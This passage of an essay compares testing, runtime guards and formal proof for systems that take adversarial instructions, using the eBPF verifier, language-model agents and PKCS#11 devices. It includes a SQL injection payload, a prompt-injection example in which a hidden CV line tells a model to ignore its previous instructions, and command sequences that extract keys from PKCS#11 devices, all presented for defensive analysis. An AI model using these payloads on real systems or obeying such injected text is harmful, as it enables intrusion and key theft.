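# Formal specification versus testing for assuring systems that take adversarial instructions

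## Systems that take instructions from strangers, and three ways to assure them

Some software carries out instructions from people whom its makers do not know and cannot trust. An operating-system kernel runs small programs that users load into it. A device that stores a bank's secret keys answers commands from any computer that can reach it. A language-model agent reads a stranger's email and acts on it. An adversarial instruction is one that an attacker may have written. The system's interface is the set of commands or actions through which outsiders can affect it. Assuring the system means finding good grounds to believe that nothing arriving through the interface can make it do what its owner forbids.

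Engineers try to assure these systems in three ways. They test the system, install guards that check instructions or actions as they arrive, and write a mathematical specification and prove that the system meets it.

Systems that take instructions from strangers are harder to assure than software that merely processes data, because an opponent picks the input. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (1972), written for the US Air Force, James P. Anderson wrote that the makers of commercial operating systems had imagined only a benign environment, so their controls guarded against little besides accidents. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972) describes a malicious user probing for flaws with out-of-place commands, nonsense parameters and unexpected interruptions. A fault that ordinary users would meet once in a billion runs hardly matters for reliability,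 but an attacker who finds it can trigger it on every run.

### Data that becomes a command

The attacker may not even need permission to give commands. Many systems receive commands and data through one channel, and data can then pass for a command. The best-known case is SQL injection, an attack on programs that query a database in the language SQL. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a web-security foundation, has an example that, with quotation marks added around the name, looks like this:

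```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = '<text the visitor typed>'
```

The program pastes the visitor's text into the query and sends the result to the database. Suppose the visitor types `tom' or '1'='1`. The database receives:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
```

The quotation mark after "tom" closes the name, and the rest of the text becomes part of the query. Since 1 equals 1 in every row, the database returns every customer's balance. The cure is a parameterized query:

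```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?
```

In a parameterized query, the program defines the whole query first and supplies the name separately, and the database treats the name only as a value. Given the same text, the database looks for a customer whose name is literally `tom' or '1'='1`. This works without anyone having to recognise the text as an attack, which is why OWASP strongly discourages the alternative of escaping, in which the program tries to neutralise dangerous characters before pasting the text into the query. CISA and the FBI's *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024) also describes input sanitization as brittle and often easy to bypass. Parameters cannot stand in for the name of a table or column, so the program has to choose those names from a fixed list.

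Parameterized queries prevent SQL injection only where developers use them. MySQL has supported them through prepared statements since 2004, yet SQL injection ranks second in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), up from third the year before.

Prompt injection exploits a similar confusion in language models. Someone places text in material a model reads so that the model obeys it as an instruction. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter's system that asks a model to score a CV in which the candidate has hidden a line telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the application. David C warns against expecting the SQL remedy to carry over, because a database handles instructions and data differently, while a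 language model receives both as one sequence of tokens (words and fragments of words) and predicts the next.

The parameterized query works because SQL has a grammar, which lets a parser tell code from data. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) point out in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that natural language has no such grammar. Developers also train models to follow instructions wherever they appear. They can mark off the untrusted part with delimiters, role labels or a warning, which is useful but creates no hard boundary, according to *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026). The marks are more tokens whose meaning the model has to infer.

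Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, have tried to turn this observation into a theorem. A model of the usual kind converts each token into a list of numbers by one fixed table, whoever wrote the token. Imagine a guesser who sees one of the model's internal representations and must say whether it came from the trusted instructions or from an outsider's text. If both are equally likely beforehand, the best possible guesser errs with probability

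P = ½ (1 − TV),

where TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the two kinds of representation have identical distributions and 1 if they never overlap. Any overlap leaves some error. Outside text also feeds into the computation that selects the model's actions, and training can cover only finitely many of the ways to encode a request. Pant and colleagues conclude that nothing inside such a model can guarantee that its decisions to refuse, or to call a tool, depend only on what the outside text means and never on how the attacker has encoded it.

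How much this proves depends on the overlap. The initial lists of numbers overlap trivially, since "the" gets the same list in an instruction and in an email. The proof assumes that the deeper representations, on which the model's decisions rest, also overlap. The theorem is perhaps best read as an exact statement of what a designer would have to rule out. It shows that there is no guarantee, but not that a particular attack will succeed against a particular model. It also doesn't cover designs in which a separate program outside the model decides which actions go ahead.

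### Two running examples

eBPF is a facility of the Linux kernel, the part of the operating system that controls the whole machine. It arrived in kernel version 3.18 in December 2014, according to *The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (2024), and lets users add their own programs to a running kernel, for instance to filter network traffic. A program arrives as bytecode, a list of simple generic instructions, and passes through three stages. The verifier examines it before it runs, following the possible paths and keeping track of the values each register (a small storage slot) could hold. eBPF Docs' *Verifier* illustrates this with a register known to lie between 10 and 30. At the instruction "if R3 > 20" the verifier splits its analysis in two, with a range of 21 to 30 on one branch and 10 to 20 on the other. It rejects the program unless it can establish that every path ends and every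 memory access stays within bounds. Next, the just-in-time (JIT) compiler translates the bytecode into machine code. Finally the program executes in the runtime, where it calls kernel functions and shares tables of data with other software. Each stage relies on the others, as Chen, Ming and colleagues (2026), in *eBPF Security in the Wild*, explain: a correct verdict from the verifier is worth little if the JIT compiler changes the program's meaning, and developers have had to fix vulnerabilities in all three stages. By default only privileged processes may load eBPF programs at all. *eBPF Documentation* also describes the verifier as a safety tool and not a security tool, meaning that it checks whether a program is safe to run and does not ask what the program is for.

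The other example is a language-model agent, a model joined to ordinary software that can act on its behalf. The software gives the model a user's request and a list of tools. The model produces a tool call, such as "send this message to this address". The software runs the tool, adds the result to the text, and calls the model again, until the model produces a final answer. Any tool result, such as a web page, support ticket or email, may contain an attacker's words. Narisetty and colleagues give the usual assumptions, which are that the attacker controls at least one source of text, knows the design and its defences, and can revise an attack against them, but cannot alter the model's weights or the software that enforces the rules. The agent's privileges make it dangerous. David C calls it an "inherently confusable deputy", after an older term for a privileged program that a less privileged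 party tricks into acting for it.

A checker can work out what an eBPF program would do before it runs because the program has an exact meaning, unlike an English sentence in an email. In an agent, the first thing with an exact meaning is usually the tool call the model produces, and most attempts at precise rules begin there.

### What each method lets its user claim

Testing means running the system on chosen inputs and watching for failures. In fuzzing, a program generates very many inputs automatically. Differential testing runs the same inputs through two implementations, or through a program and its specification, and looks for disagreements. Testers of language-model systems usually report an attack success rate, the share of attempts, or of attacked tasks, in which the attacker's goal is reached. The number means most when the attack is adaptive, that is, when the testers have designed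 and revised it against the particular defence. A failure found this way is conclusive. A clean result supports only the claim "we found no failure". Anderson made the point about the "tiger teams" that attacked military computers to test them: an unsuccessful attack leaves the security of the system unknown, and the result depends heavily on who was on the team. (No team he knew of had failed.)

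A runtime guard inspects instructions or actions as they arrive and blocks some of them. A rule-based guard uses fixed rules to decide what to block, while a model-based guard uses a learned model, such as a classifier for injected instructions. The eBPF verifier is a rule-based guard that inspects a whole program once, when it is loaded. Guards around agents more often inspect each tool call. A guard's log is evidence that it blocked a particular action, but determining whether it would block the next attack still requires testing or proof.

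Formal methods begin with a specification, a precise and usually mathematical statement of what a system may and may not do. It can be as plain as "no accepted program writes outside its buffer", or it can compare whole runs of the system, as noninterference does. Formal verification is a machine-checked proof that a design or program meets its specification for every input. The claim has the form

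if A holds, then for every input x, the system's behaviour on x satisfies S,

where S is the specification and A collects the assumptions. "No input can cause this" is therefore always short for "no input can cause this, given these assumptions". The trusted base is everything that the guarantee takes to be correct without proof, such as the compiler, the hardware and the specification itself. If S leaves out something the owner cares about, the proof is silent on it.

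In model checking, an engineer writes a model of the design, and a tool explores every state the model can reach. If a state breaks the specification, the tool reports the steps that led to it, so model checking is a good way to find design errors before anyone writes the code. But the result holds for the model, and the finished program may differ. A refinement proof closes that gap by showing that a more abstract specification allows everything a concrete program does.

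The most important property of a checker is soundness, which means that it never accepts anything that breaks its rule. A sound checker may still reject harmless things. *Keel* (Cai, Chang and Nagarakatte, 2026) gives an example from eBPF. A program writes two records, one after the other, into an 800-byte buffer. The first is n bytes long, where n is between 0 and 800. The second starts at byte n and is at most 800 − n bytes long, so it ends at or before byte 800. The verifier does not track that the second record's start and length both depend on n, only that each is between 0 and 800. It adds the two ranges, calculates that the write might reach byte 1,600, and rejects a safe program.

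### The reference monitor

A guard lets us assure a small system instead of a large one, which helps only if the small one is trustworthy. Anderson described an ideal guard for shared computers, the reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what the program's user may do. Any mechanism that implements it must be tamperproof, always invoked, and small enough to analyse and test completely. In the second volume, Anderson equates being small enough with being capable of proof.

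Anderson applied these severe demands to GCOS III, a commercial operating system for a Honeywell machine. The hardware confined each user's program to its own memory, but it suspended this check whenever the operating system acted for a user, so the guard was not always invoked. Counting the operating system as part of the guard would not help, because it and its supporting software had 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, far too many to analyse. Several successful penetrations had already shown that the operating system was not tamperproof.

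Anderson's demands also apply to agents. Narisetty and colleagues treat a guard at the tool call as a reference monitor and use the demands to classify its failures. If information can leak by a route the guard does not inspect, the guard fails the demand that it always be invoked. If a language model writes the guard's rules, the guard is harder to verify.

### Proving a guard, and testing what the proof assumes

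The three methods combine well, though they are often set against each other, and eBPF has some of the clearest examples. One is a proof about part of a guard, the Linux verifier. To follow a program's values, the verifier records whether each bit of a number is 0, 1 or unknown, and it needs rules for arithmetic on these partly known numbers. *Sound, Precise, and Fast Abstract Interpretation with Tristate Numbers* (2021) supplied a sound multiplication rule that was faster than the kernel's, and Linux adopted it.

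Keel goes further. It builds on an earlier project, the eBPF Certificate Framework (BCF), which lets the kernel accept safe programs that the verifier would otherwise reject, like the one with the 800-byte buffer. When the verifier cannot establish a safety condition C on a path that the program takes under condition P, it generates the formula P ∧ ¬C, which means that the program takes this path and the access is unsafe. Software outside the kernel then looks for a proof that the formula can never be true. For the buffer program, the proof has 33 steps and takes up 852 bytes. A checker inside the kernel, about 5,000 lines of C, checks each step, so the checker must be trusted but the software that found the proof need not be.

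Cai and colleagues found 13 previously unknown bugs in the unverified checker while writing a formal description of it. Some of its rules were mathematically wrong, and for some steps it accepted the user's conclusion without checking it. An attacker could use a forged proof to get an unsafe program past the kernel. The researchers' replacement, Keel, is specified in Lean, a language for machine-checked proofs, and they proved that the specified checker accepts a certificate only if the formula is impossible. A refinement proof shows that the C code meets this specification, and further proofs bound the time and memory it can use. Inside the kernel, Keel ran 1.3 times as fast as the unverified checker.

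Keel still has a considerable trusted base, which includes the C compiler, the program that prints the C code from Lean, the description of the kernel functions that Keel calls, and the part of the eBPF verifier that writes the formula. If the verifier writes the wrong formula, Keel will correctly check a proof of the wrong statement. Tests that run the compiled code can expose a faulty compiler or printer, which the proof cannot do. Cai and colleagues ran Keel on 1,891 stand-alone certificates and, in differential tests, on 64 million fuzzed ones. It accepted every certificate in the stand-alone set that the old checker accepted, along with 16 valid ones that the old checker had rejected, and it rejected the forgeries.

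## What theory says each approach can promise

### What clean tests show

How much can a clean run of tests establish? When testers draw their inputs at random, statistics gives an exact answer. Suppose a system fails on a fraction p of inputs and the testers try n of them, each drawn independently. All n pass with probability (1 − p)^n. If nothing fails, the testers can rule out, at 95% confidence, any p large enough to make such a clean run less than 5% likely. The borderline value satisfies

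(1 − p)^n = 0.05.

Taking logarithms gives n ln(1 − p) = ln 0.05 ≈ −3. For small p, ln(1 − p) is very nearly −p, so

p ≈ 3/n.

By the rule of three, a tester who runs 3,000 trials without a failure can say with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below 3/3,000, or 0.1%. *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred* (Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues, 1995) recommended the rule to surgeons reporting a series of operations without a complication, if the series has more than 30 patients.

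But p is the failure rate on inputs like the ones the testers drew. That rate is useful for a surgeon, whose next patient will probably resemble earlier ones, but not for a system whose attacker chooses the inputs. If a program misbehaves on exactly one 64-bit number, random tests would need about 18 billion billion tries, on average, to hit it. Three thousand clean trials would correctly show that the failure rate is below 0.1%, but an attacker who reads the code and finds the number would succeed on the first attempt.

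Ross Anderson and Roger Needham, in *Programming Satan's Computer*, described the security engineer's task as programming a computer whose answers are "subtly and maliciously wrong at the most inconvenient possible moment". Their subject was cryptographic protocols, which may exchange only two to five messages, yet people still found bugs in them years after publication. Bruce Schneier (2001), in *Foreword to Security Engineering by Ross Anderson*, contrasted Satan's computer with "Murphy's computer", which suffers only random errors and mistakes, the kind of failure to which the rule of three applies.

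Fuzzing fits the rule even less well, because its results are not independent draws. *An Analysis of How Many Undiscovered Vulnerabilities Remain in Information Systems* (2023) considers a fuzzer that runs for 300 hours and finds nothing. An ecologist can estimate the number of fish in a lake by catching two samples and counting the fish caught both times. This method fails for bugs because two crashes may have the same cause, and because it assumes that program outputs are independent when they are not. *STADS* (2018) nevertheless proposes estimating the probability that the fuzzer's next input will take a new path through the program, and treats this as an upper bound on the probability that the input reveals a new vulnerability. In one campaign, the estimate was about 2 in 100 million after 100 hours. At that rate, a fuzzer running 1,000 inputs a second would still find a new path about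 every 14 hours. The estimate can help an engineer decide whether to keep the fuzzer running, but it does not limit what an attacker with a different tool might find.

An attacker can also try again. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others, then k attempts all fail with probability (1 − p)^k, and at least one succeeds with probability

1 − (1 − p)^k.

With p = 1% and k = 100, this comes to 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. A guard that stops 99% of attacks is therefore poor protection against someone who can send a hundred emails. Even after 3,000 clean trials, p could still be 0.1%, which would give an attacker with 1,000 attempts about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. To hold the risk from 1,000 attempts to 1%, p must be about 0.001%, and by the rule of three it takes 300,000 clean trials to show that.

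The 63% figure assumes that the attempts are independent. If the 1% is instead an average over tasks, and the attack always works on one task in a hundred and never on the rest, then a hundred attempts on one randomly chosen task have a 1% chance of success, the same as a single attempt. An attacker who learns from each failure may do better than 63%. Testers therefore have to measure the effect of repetition directly, because they can't infer it from the single-attempt rate.

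### What a guard can enforce

Unlike a test, a runtime guard has the advantage of acting on the attacker's actual input, not the tester's guess at it. Its guarantees depend on what it can observe. Fred B. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) works out the limits of guards that watch a program step by step and stop it when it is about to break a rule. Firewalls and reference monitors are examples. Such a guard can observe the steps so far, but not what the program would do next or would have done with other inputs. The eBPF verifier is not in this class, because it analyses a program's code before the program runs.

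Schneider derived three conditions that a rule must meet for such a guard to enforce it. First, whether a run is allowed must depend on that run alone. Second, if the rule forbids a partial run, it must also forbid every continuation of that run, because the program might stop before correcting the violation. Third, every forbidden run must break the rule after a finite number of steps, or the guard would never have a point at which to act. A rule that meets all three conditions is a safety property, which is roughly a rule that some identifiable bad thing never happens.

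A guard that enforces the rule "no message after a file read" needs a memory with two states. It starts in "no file read" and moves to "file read" when the program reads a file. In the second state, it stops the program at any attempt to send a message. Two guards of this sort working together enforce both of their rules.

"Every customer who pays is eventually served" is not a safety property. However long the customer has waited, service may still come, so no partial run breaks the rule. A guard can stop a seller that has taken payment from doing anything except deliver, but it can't make the seller deliver. Around an agent, similarly, a guard can block a payment to a stranger but can't ensure that the agent finishes its user's task. Even some safety properties are out of reach. "Nobody waits more than ten seconds for a resource" has an identifiable bad moment, but the guard has no power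 to stop the clock. If the rule counts the program's steps instead of seconds, a guard can enforce it by halting the program. (Guards that can insert or suppress actions, as well as halt the program, can enforce some rules that are not safety properties.)

Noninterference fails the first condition. It is the property that what an observer sees does not depend on inputs that the observer should not learn or be affected by. Consider a program that reads a confidential file about a merger and then posts its user's availability on a public calendar. Two versions of it might behave like this:

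| | The file says the merger is off | The file says the merger is on |
|---|---|---|
| Program A posts | "Free on Friday" | "Free on Friday" |
| Program B posts | "Free on Friday" | "Busy on Friday" |

Program A satisfies noninterference. Program B leaks the secret, because anyone who knows how it works can tell from the calendar whether the merger is on. When the merger is off, a guard monitoring program B observes a file read and then the post "Free on Friday". It would observe the same thing with program A, so it can't stop one without stopping the other. When the merger is on, the guard observes the post "Busy on Friday", but a program that posted those words whatever the file said would also satisfy noninterference. Each of program B's runs is acceptable by itself. The leak consists in the difference between them, so a guard watching only one run can't detect it.

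Prompt injection raises a similar problem. Whether a stranger's email influenced an agent's payment depends on what the agent would have done if the email had been different, and the actual run doesn't show that.

A guard can still prevent the leak by enforcing a stricter rule. "No post after reading the file" is a safety property, and enforcing it stops program B, but it also stops program A. Schneider observes that all guards of this class that are meant to prevent information flow enforce some rule that implies the absence of a leak but isn't equivalent to it. Letting program A run while rejecting program B requires analyzing the programs themselves, and researchers have since proved noninterference theorems for some agent designs.

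All this assumes that the guard observes every relevant step, can stop the program, and is safe from tampering. These assumptions are close to James Anderson's requirements for a reference monitor. The first may be the hardest to meet, because a large program can have many ways to send a message, some of them hard to find, and a rule about sending covers only those its author identified.

Under this theory, a model-based guard that blocks every step its classifier flags enforces the rule "no flagged step" perfectly, and that rule is a safety property. But the owner wanted "no harmful step", and testing is needed to find out how far the two rules differ.

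### Why Rice's theorem leaves room for proof

A proof starts from the program's code, so it can cover every possible run, including comparisons between runs. In the early 1950s, Henry Gordon Rice proved a limit on automating such checks. If a property concerns what programs do rather than how their text looks, and some programs have it while others lack it, then no procedure can correctly decide for every program whether it has the property. The theorem still allows proofs about particular programs.

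The theorem follows from the halting problem, the fact that no procedure can tell for every program whether it will eventually stop. *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from the Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER) in Cambridge, illustrates the link with a few lines of code:

```
def program(input):
    program2(input)
    unsafe_function()
```

Consider a program that runs `program2` and then calls an unsafe function. If `program2` does nothing unsafe itself, the program reaches the unsafe function exactly when `program2` stops. A perfect safety checker could therefore solve the halting problem, which is impossible, so no perfect safety checker can exist.

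CSER was answering Alfonseca and colleagues, who had argued on these grounds that nobody can guarantee the safety of a superintelligent machine. CSER replies that Rice's theorem rules out a procedure that works for all programs, while engineers want to know about particular ones. Similarly, no procedure can settle every mathematical statement, but mathematicians can still prove Pythagoras's theorem. Alfonseca and colleagues had allowed for this objection by assuming that the machine might run arbitrary programs as part of its work. CSER responds that engineers could build a machine that doesn't run arbitrary programs.

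A kernel that accepts uploaded programs doesn't have that option, because it is meant to run other people's programs. It has to give something up, and the eBPF verifier does so by rejecting some safe programs, like the one with the 800-byte buffer. The certificates that Keel checks recover some of these. They apply proof-carrying code, an older idea that Schneider describes, in which a program arrives with a proof of its own safety.

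Designers can also restrict the language so that every program in it has the property, and then no tool has to check for it. *Do Expressive Programming Languages Always Have Undefined Behavior?*, a post on the computer scientist John Regehr's blog, explains this for undefined behaviour, meaning operations such as division by zero to which a language like C assigns no result. No tool can decide for every C program whether it will ever perform such an operation, but the problem disappears if the language defines a result for every operation. The post adds that designers of realistic languages seldom do this because it takes a lot of work. A language for writing a guard's rules can be much smaller, so restricting it should take less work.

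### Ruling out attacks nobody listed

Adam Chlipala, a computer scientist at MIT who works on programming languages and verification, has argued on the blog *Structure and Guarantees* that if a proof covers every input, it ought to cover attacks that the proof's author never thought of.

1. Someone has proved that a program meets its specification for every input. The specification forbids at least one behaviour, call it BAD, that the machine could carry out if it ran the right code.
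2. Suppose some input let an attacker run code of their own choosing. The attacker could choose code that does BAD.
3. The program would then have an input that leads to BAD, which contradicts the proof. So no such input exists.

Chlipala's example is an internet service that adds positive numbers. Its specification might require only that every output be positive. A proof that the service meets this specification also rules out code injection, because an attacker who could inject code could make the service return zero. No attacker would want a zero, but being able to produce one would contradict the proof. Security normally favours the attacker, who needs only one vulnerability, while the defender must fix them all. Here the defender rules out a whole class of attacks without having to list buffer overflows, injected scripts or techniques not yet invented.

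The argument is valid, but it excludes only flaws that give an attacker full control. Suppose a smaller flaw lets an attacker make the service return a secret key, stored as a number elsewhere in its memory. The key is positive, so the service can still be proved to meet its specification. A specification requiring the correct sum would also exclude this flaw.

Chlipala also considers a shopping agent, whose specification might allow only orders the user has explicitly approved, or merely forbid orders above the user's credit card limit. Either specification is enough to rule out a takeover of the agent's code. But under the second, an injected instruction could still make the agent buy the attacker's goods for any sum below the limit. Prompt injection rarely needs arbitrary code, because it works by getting a model to choose badly among the actions it is allowed to take.

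The proof also depends on the machine model, a mathematical description of what the hardware and the programming language do. The proof covers every input to that idealised machine, but an attacker may be able to exploit behaviour the model omits, such as a memory chip that sometimes flips a bit or a response time that reveals a secret. *An Analysis of How Many Undiscovered Vulnerabilities Remain in Information Systems* groups program verification with fuzzing, as a tool that gives little or no evidence about vulnerabilities still undiscovered. That judgement is fair for vulnerabilities that wouldn't violate the specification, but too harsh for those that would, since a proof excludes them if its assumptions hold.

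Chlipala extends the argument to learned components that are implementation details the specification never mentions. Corrupting such a component either changes nothing that matters or would break the specification, and the proof rules out the second case. The argument doesn't help when the system relies on the learned component to meet the specification, because nobody can prove in advance what that component will do. This limitation applies to an agent whose model decides which actions to take with no separate program to check them.

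### NIST's proof about guardrails

In June 2026 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) announced a proof that appears to set a much more general limit. According to NIST's summary, no finite set of guardrails is universally robust against adversarial prompts. Apostol Vassilev, a scientist at NIST, published the result in the magazine *IEEE Security & Privacy* as *Robust AI Security and Alignment* (2026). Vassilev's December 2025 manuscript of the same title contains the full proof.

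The set-up has a policy that marks some prompts as unacceptable, and a checker C. Given a statement T and a proposed proof p, the checker returns 1 only if T is true and p proves it. The theorem is that

for every checker C there is a true statement T such that C(T, p) ≠ 1 for every p.

Vassilev first assumes an ideal system that accepts prompts of any length and has unlimited computing power. Such a system has infinitely many unacceptable prompts, because an attacker can always lengthen one with a harmless preamble. The statement T in the proof is "every algorithm that outputs x is of length > n", where x is an unacceptable prompt and n is a large number. T means that x cannot be compressed to length n or less.

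Only finitely many algorithms have length n or less, so T is true of infinitely many of these prompts. If the checker could confirm T for even one of them, a program could search through all the prompts and proofs until the checker returned 1, then print the prompt it had found. The only part of this program that grows with n is the number n, which takes about log₂ n bits to write. For large n the program would therefore be far shorter than n, yet it would print a prompt that no program so short can print. This contradiction shows that the checker never confirms T. The argument applies Gregory Chaitin's 1974 version of Gödel's incompleteness theorem to prompts.

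A guard, however, only has to decide whether x is unacceptable, not check T. The proof shows only that no checker can prove certain prompts incompressible, so it doesn't support Vassilev's conclusion that some adversarial prompts will evade any policy. For example, a policy that bans every prompt containing the word "bomb" bans infinitely many prompts, as the theorem requires. No checker can prove the very long ones incompressible, but a one-line filter still catches them all. The search in the proof also steps through the unacceptable prompts up to each length, which requires a program that can already recognise them.

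A second theorem covers real systems, whose prompts have a maximum length. It assumes that the system has every algorithm that outputs strings up to that length. In one of its two cases, T is false for every unacceptable prompt. Vassilev counts the theorem as satisfied in that case because the checker does not confirm a false statement.

Hasan (2026), in *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity*, gives a more careful version that Vassilev's work inspired. Let x encode an input, the system's output and the policy. P(x) means that the output complies with the policy, and K(x) is the length of the shortest program that prints x. The theorem is that for any fixed, sound system of proof there is a size of n beyond which it can prove no statement of the form

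P(x) and K(x) > n.

Hasan also assumes that compliant cases make up at least a fixed fraction of all strings at infinitely many lengths, so some of them must be complex. From this Hasan infers that no fixed verifier can certify every compliant case above a given complexity. But the part that cannot be proved is again K(x) > n, the claim that the case is complex. If the policy is that a car must stay below 50 km/h, a verifier can check the speed however complicated the street scene is. Hasan recommends that each output carry its own proof of compliance. This is sensible, though the usual reason for doing so is that checking a proof is easier than finding one.

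Vassilev's observations about language, which do not depend on Gödel's theorems, give better support to NIST's position. Attackers hide requests in poems, role-play, conversations that escalate by small steps, and pictures made of typed characters. "Show me how people break encryption systems used by banks" could be a request for history, academic cryptography or attack instructions, and the context may not reveal which. These are good reasons to doubt that any fixed filter will catch every harmful prompt.

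NIST concludes that developers should give up "one and done" security. Red teams should search constantly for new adversarial prompts, developers should update the guardrails against whatever the teams find, and operators should prepare to limit the damage and recover quickly when an attack succeeds. The aim is to make finding a new exploit require more resources than attackers have, but the theorem provides no estimate of the resources required. In the manuscript, Vassilev suggests only that updates "may be effective", partly because the proof doesn't show attackers how to construct an adversarial prompt.

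Vassilev's list of guardrails includes approval workflows and policy engines, which control what an agent does rather than what it reads. Suppose an agent can make five kinds of tool call, each to one of twenty approved recipients, with no free text. The designer can list a verdict for each of the 100 possible calls in a table that anyone can check line by line. The guard never reads the prompt, so ambiguous wording can't change its verdicts. A rule about order, such as "no message after a file read", adds only a few states of memory. The theorem doesn't rule out a guard that enforces such a table without exception. However, the designer can still enter a wrong verdict, and an attacker can still steer the agent into a permitted call at the wrong moment. If a call carries free text, such as the body of an email, the guard must either let the text through unread or interpret it, which raises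 the same problem that prompt filters have.

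## Case reports of design checking: protocols, key-storage devices, cloud services and permission rules

A table that lists a separate verdict for each tool call, like the one for an agent's 100 possible calls, can miss attacks made up of calls that look harmless one at a time. Model checking is well suited to finding these attacks because it explores sequences of calls. In a simple example, two ordinary commands are enough to steal a key from a device that stores secret keys.

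### A model with two keys

A key-storage device, such as a smartcard or a hardware module in a bank's data centre, encrypts and decrypts data for other computers without revealing its keys to them. A program refers to a key by a handle, a name that doesn't reveal the key's value. Many of these devices accept commands defined by PKCS#11, a standard from the company RSA.

Suppose a device holds two keys, K1 and K2, and accepts two commands. `wrap(K2, K1)` encrypts K1 under K2 and returns the result, so that the owner can move K1 safely to another device. `decrypt(K2, c)` decrypts the data c with K2 and returns the result. K2 has one flag that permits wrapping and another that permits decryption. The attacker has the handles of both keys and can send any command, perhaps through malware on the computer the device is plugged into. The specification is that the attacker never learns K1.

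A state of this model consists of the flags and the attacker's knowledge. Suppose both flags are on. The checker starts from the state in which the attacker knows only the handles, and tries every command. Decrypting achieves nothing yet, because the attacker has no data encrypted under K2. Wrapping leads to a second state, in which the attacker has K1 encrypted under K2. From there the checker tries every command again, and finds a violation:

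```
wrap(K2, K1)                          returns K1 encrypted under K2
decrypt(K2, K1 encrypted under K2)    returns K1
```

Both commands work correctly, but the design is faulty because it lets the same key be used for both. Clulow (2003), in *On the Security of PKCS #11*, described this attack on the standard, whose designers had written that a sensitive key "will always remain sensitive".

The obvious repair, forbidding K2 from having both flags on at once, fails if users can switch flags on and off. K2 still has three settings (neither flag, wrap only, decrypt only), and the attacker either has the wrapped copy of K1 or doesn't, which makes six states. The checker can reach all of them. In one, K2 may decrypt and the attacker already has the wrapped key, so the next command reveals K1. The attacker reaches this state by switching wrapping on, wrapping K1, switching wrapping off and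 switching decryption on.

If a flag stays on once it is turned on, only four of the six states remain reachable, and no command in any of them reveals K1. So no sequence of commands, of any length, can break the rule in this model. But the model has only two commands besides the flag switches, and real devices have many more.

### Repairing PKCS#11

In *Formal Analysis of PKCS#11*, Delaune, Kremer and Steel built a larger model of the standard's main key-management commands. After they applied both repairs, the second of which makes the flags permanent, the checker found a previously unpublished attack in 7.6 seconds. The attack uses two further commands: `encrypt`, which encrypts ordinary data, and `unwrap`, which decrypts a wrapped key and stores it in the device.

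1. The attacker makes up a key, K3, and asks the device to encrypt it under K2 as if it were ordinary data.
2. The attacker asks the device to unwrap the result. The device decrypts it and stores K3 as one of its own keys.
3. The attacker switches on wrapping for K3 and wraps K1 under it.
4. The attacker, who knows K3, decrypts K1 without the device's help.

The researchers then barred any key from both encrypting and unwrapping. The checker found the next attack in 1.9 seconds. In this attack, the attacker wraps K2 under itself and then unwraps it. The device now holds two copies of K2, each with its own flags, so one copy can wrap K1 and the other can decrypt it. After the researchers also barred any key from both wrapping and unwrapping, the checker found no attack, even with four handles for each key.

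Adding public-key pairs to the model made an attack possible again, as did a feature that the standard's designers had introduced to improve security. The feature allows a sensitive key to be set so that only a "trusted" key can wrap it, and only a security officer can approve a key as trusted. The attacker first stole the trusted key, which lacked this protection, and then used it to decrypt K1. Giving trusted keys the same protection produced a configuration with no attack in the model.

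Clulow, a specialist in these attacks, had suggested the first repair, yet it still allowed another attack. People are bad at foreseeing how a dozen simple commands will combine, but a checker can redo the whole search after every change.

The search covers only what the model includes. *Formal Analysis of PKCS#11* discusses an earlier model that gave each key a single handle, and so could not represent the attack with two copies of K2. Delaune and colleagues used a fixed number of keys and handles in their own models, and adding extra ones often exhausted the computer's 4 gigabytes of memory. They also left out the command that derives one key from another, and they treated encryption as perfect.

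One of Clulow's attacks depends on those omissions. The attacker tells the device to derive 65,536 variants of a secret key, each differing from it by a known pattern, and to encrypt the same text with each variant. The attacker then guesses keys until one produces any of the 65,536 results. For DES, an old cipher with 56-bit keys, this takes about 2^39 guesses on average, compared with about 2^55 to find one particular key. Any match reveals the original key. Clulow pointed out that, unlike the wrap-and-decrypt attack, this one works even on keys that the device does not allow to be exported.

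### From the standard to real devices

Manufacturers often restrict the standard's commands in ways they don't document, so a flaw in the standard isn't necessarily a flaw in a product. In *Attacking and Fixing PKCS#11 Security Tokens*, Bortolozzo, Centenaro and colleagues (2010) therefore used a tool, Tookan, that works out which functions each device supports, builds a model of them and passes it to a model checker. If the checker finds an attack, Tookan runs the commands on the device itself. A mistake in the model therefore can't produce a false report of a stolen key, though it can still hide a real attack.

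Of 17 commercial devices tested, nine were vulnerable and the other eight had severely restricted functions. According to secgroup's project page for Tookan, every device that could wrap sensitive keys was open to attack. The devices that resisted had dropped this function, so their owners could not use it to move a secret key to another device or keep an encrypted backup.

A later table on the project page covers 18 devices and lists the first attack Tookan found on each of the ten that were vulnerable. On three devices, the attack was a form of wrap-and-decrypt. Six others returned the value of a sensitive key on request, which the standard forbids, and one revealed a key that its owner had marked as impossible to extract. A tester with a copy of the standard could have found these seven flaws by requesting a key. They show that manufacturers had neglected basic tests, but are weak evidence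 that model checking is needed.

Bortolozzo and colleagues also produced a secure configuration that still allowed key export and needed no new cryptographic mechanisms, and they implemented it in a software simulator. In secgroup's tests, each of three patches blocked only one of three variants of the wrap-and-decrypt attack, so a secure device needed all three patches.

### A protocol that stood for 17 years

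In a network protocol the attacker has no device to command, but can intercept and forge the messages that other people's computers send. The Needham-Schroeder public-key protocol, published in 1978, lets two parties confirm each other's identity. In its short form it has three messages:

1. Alice sends Bob a fresh random number Na and her name, encrypted so that only Bob can read them.
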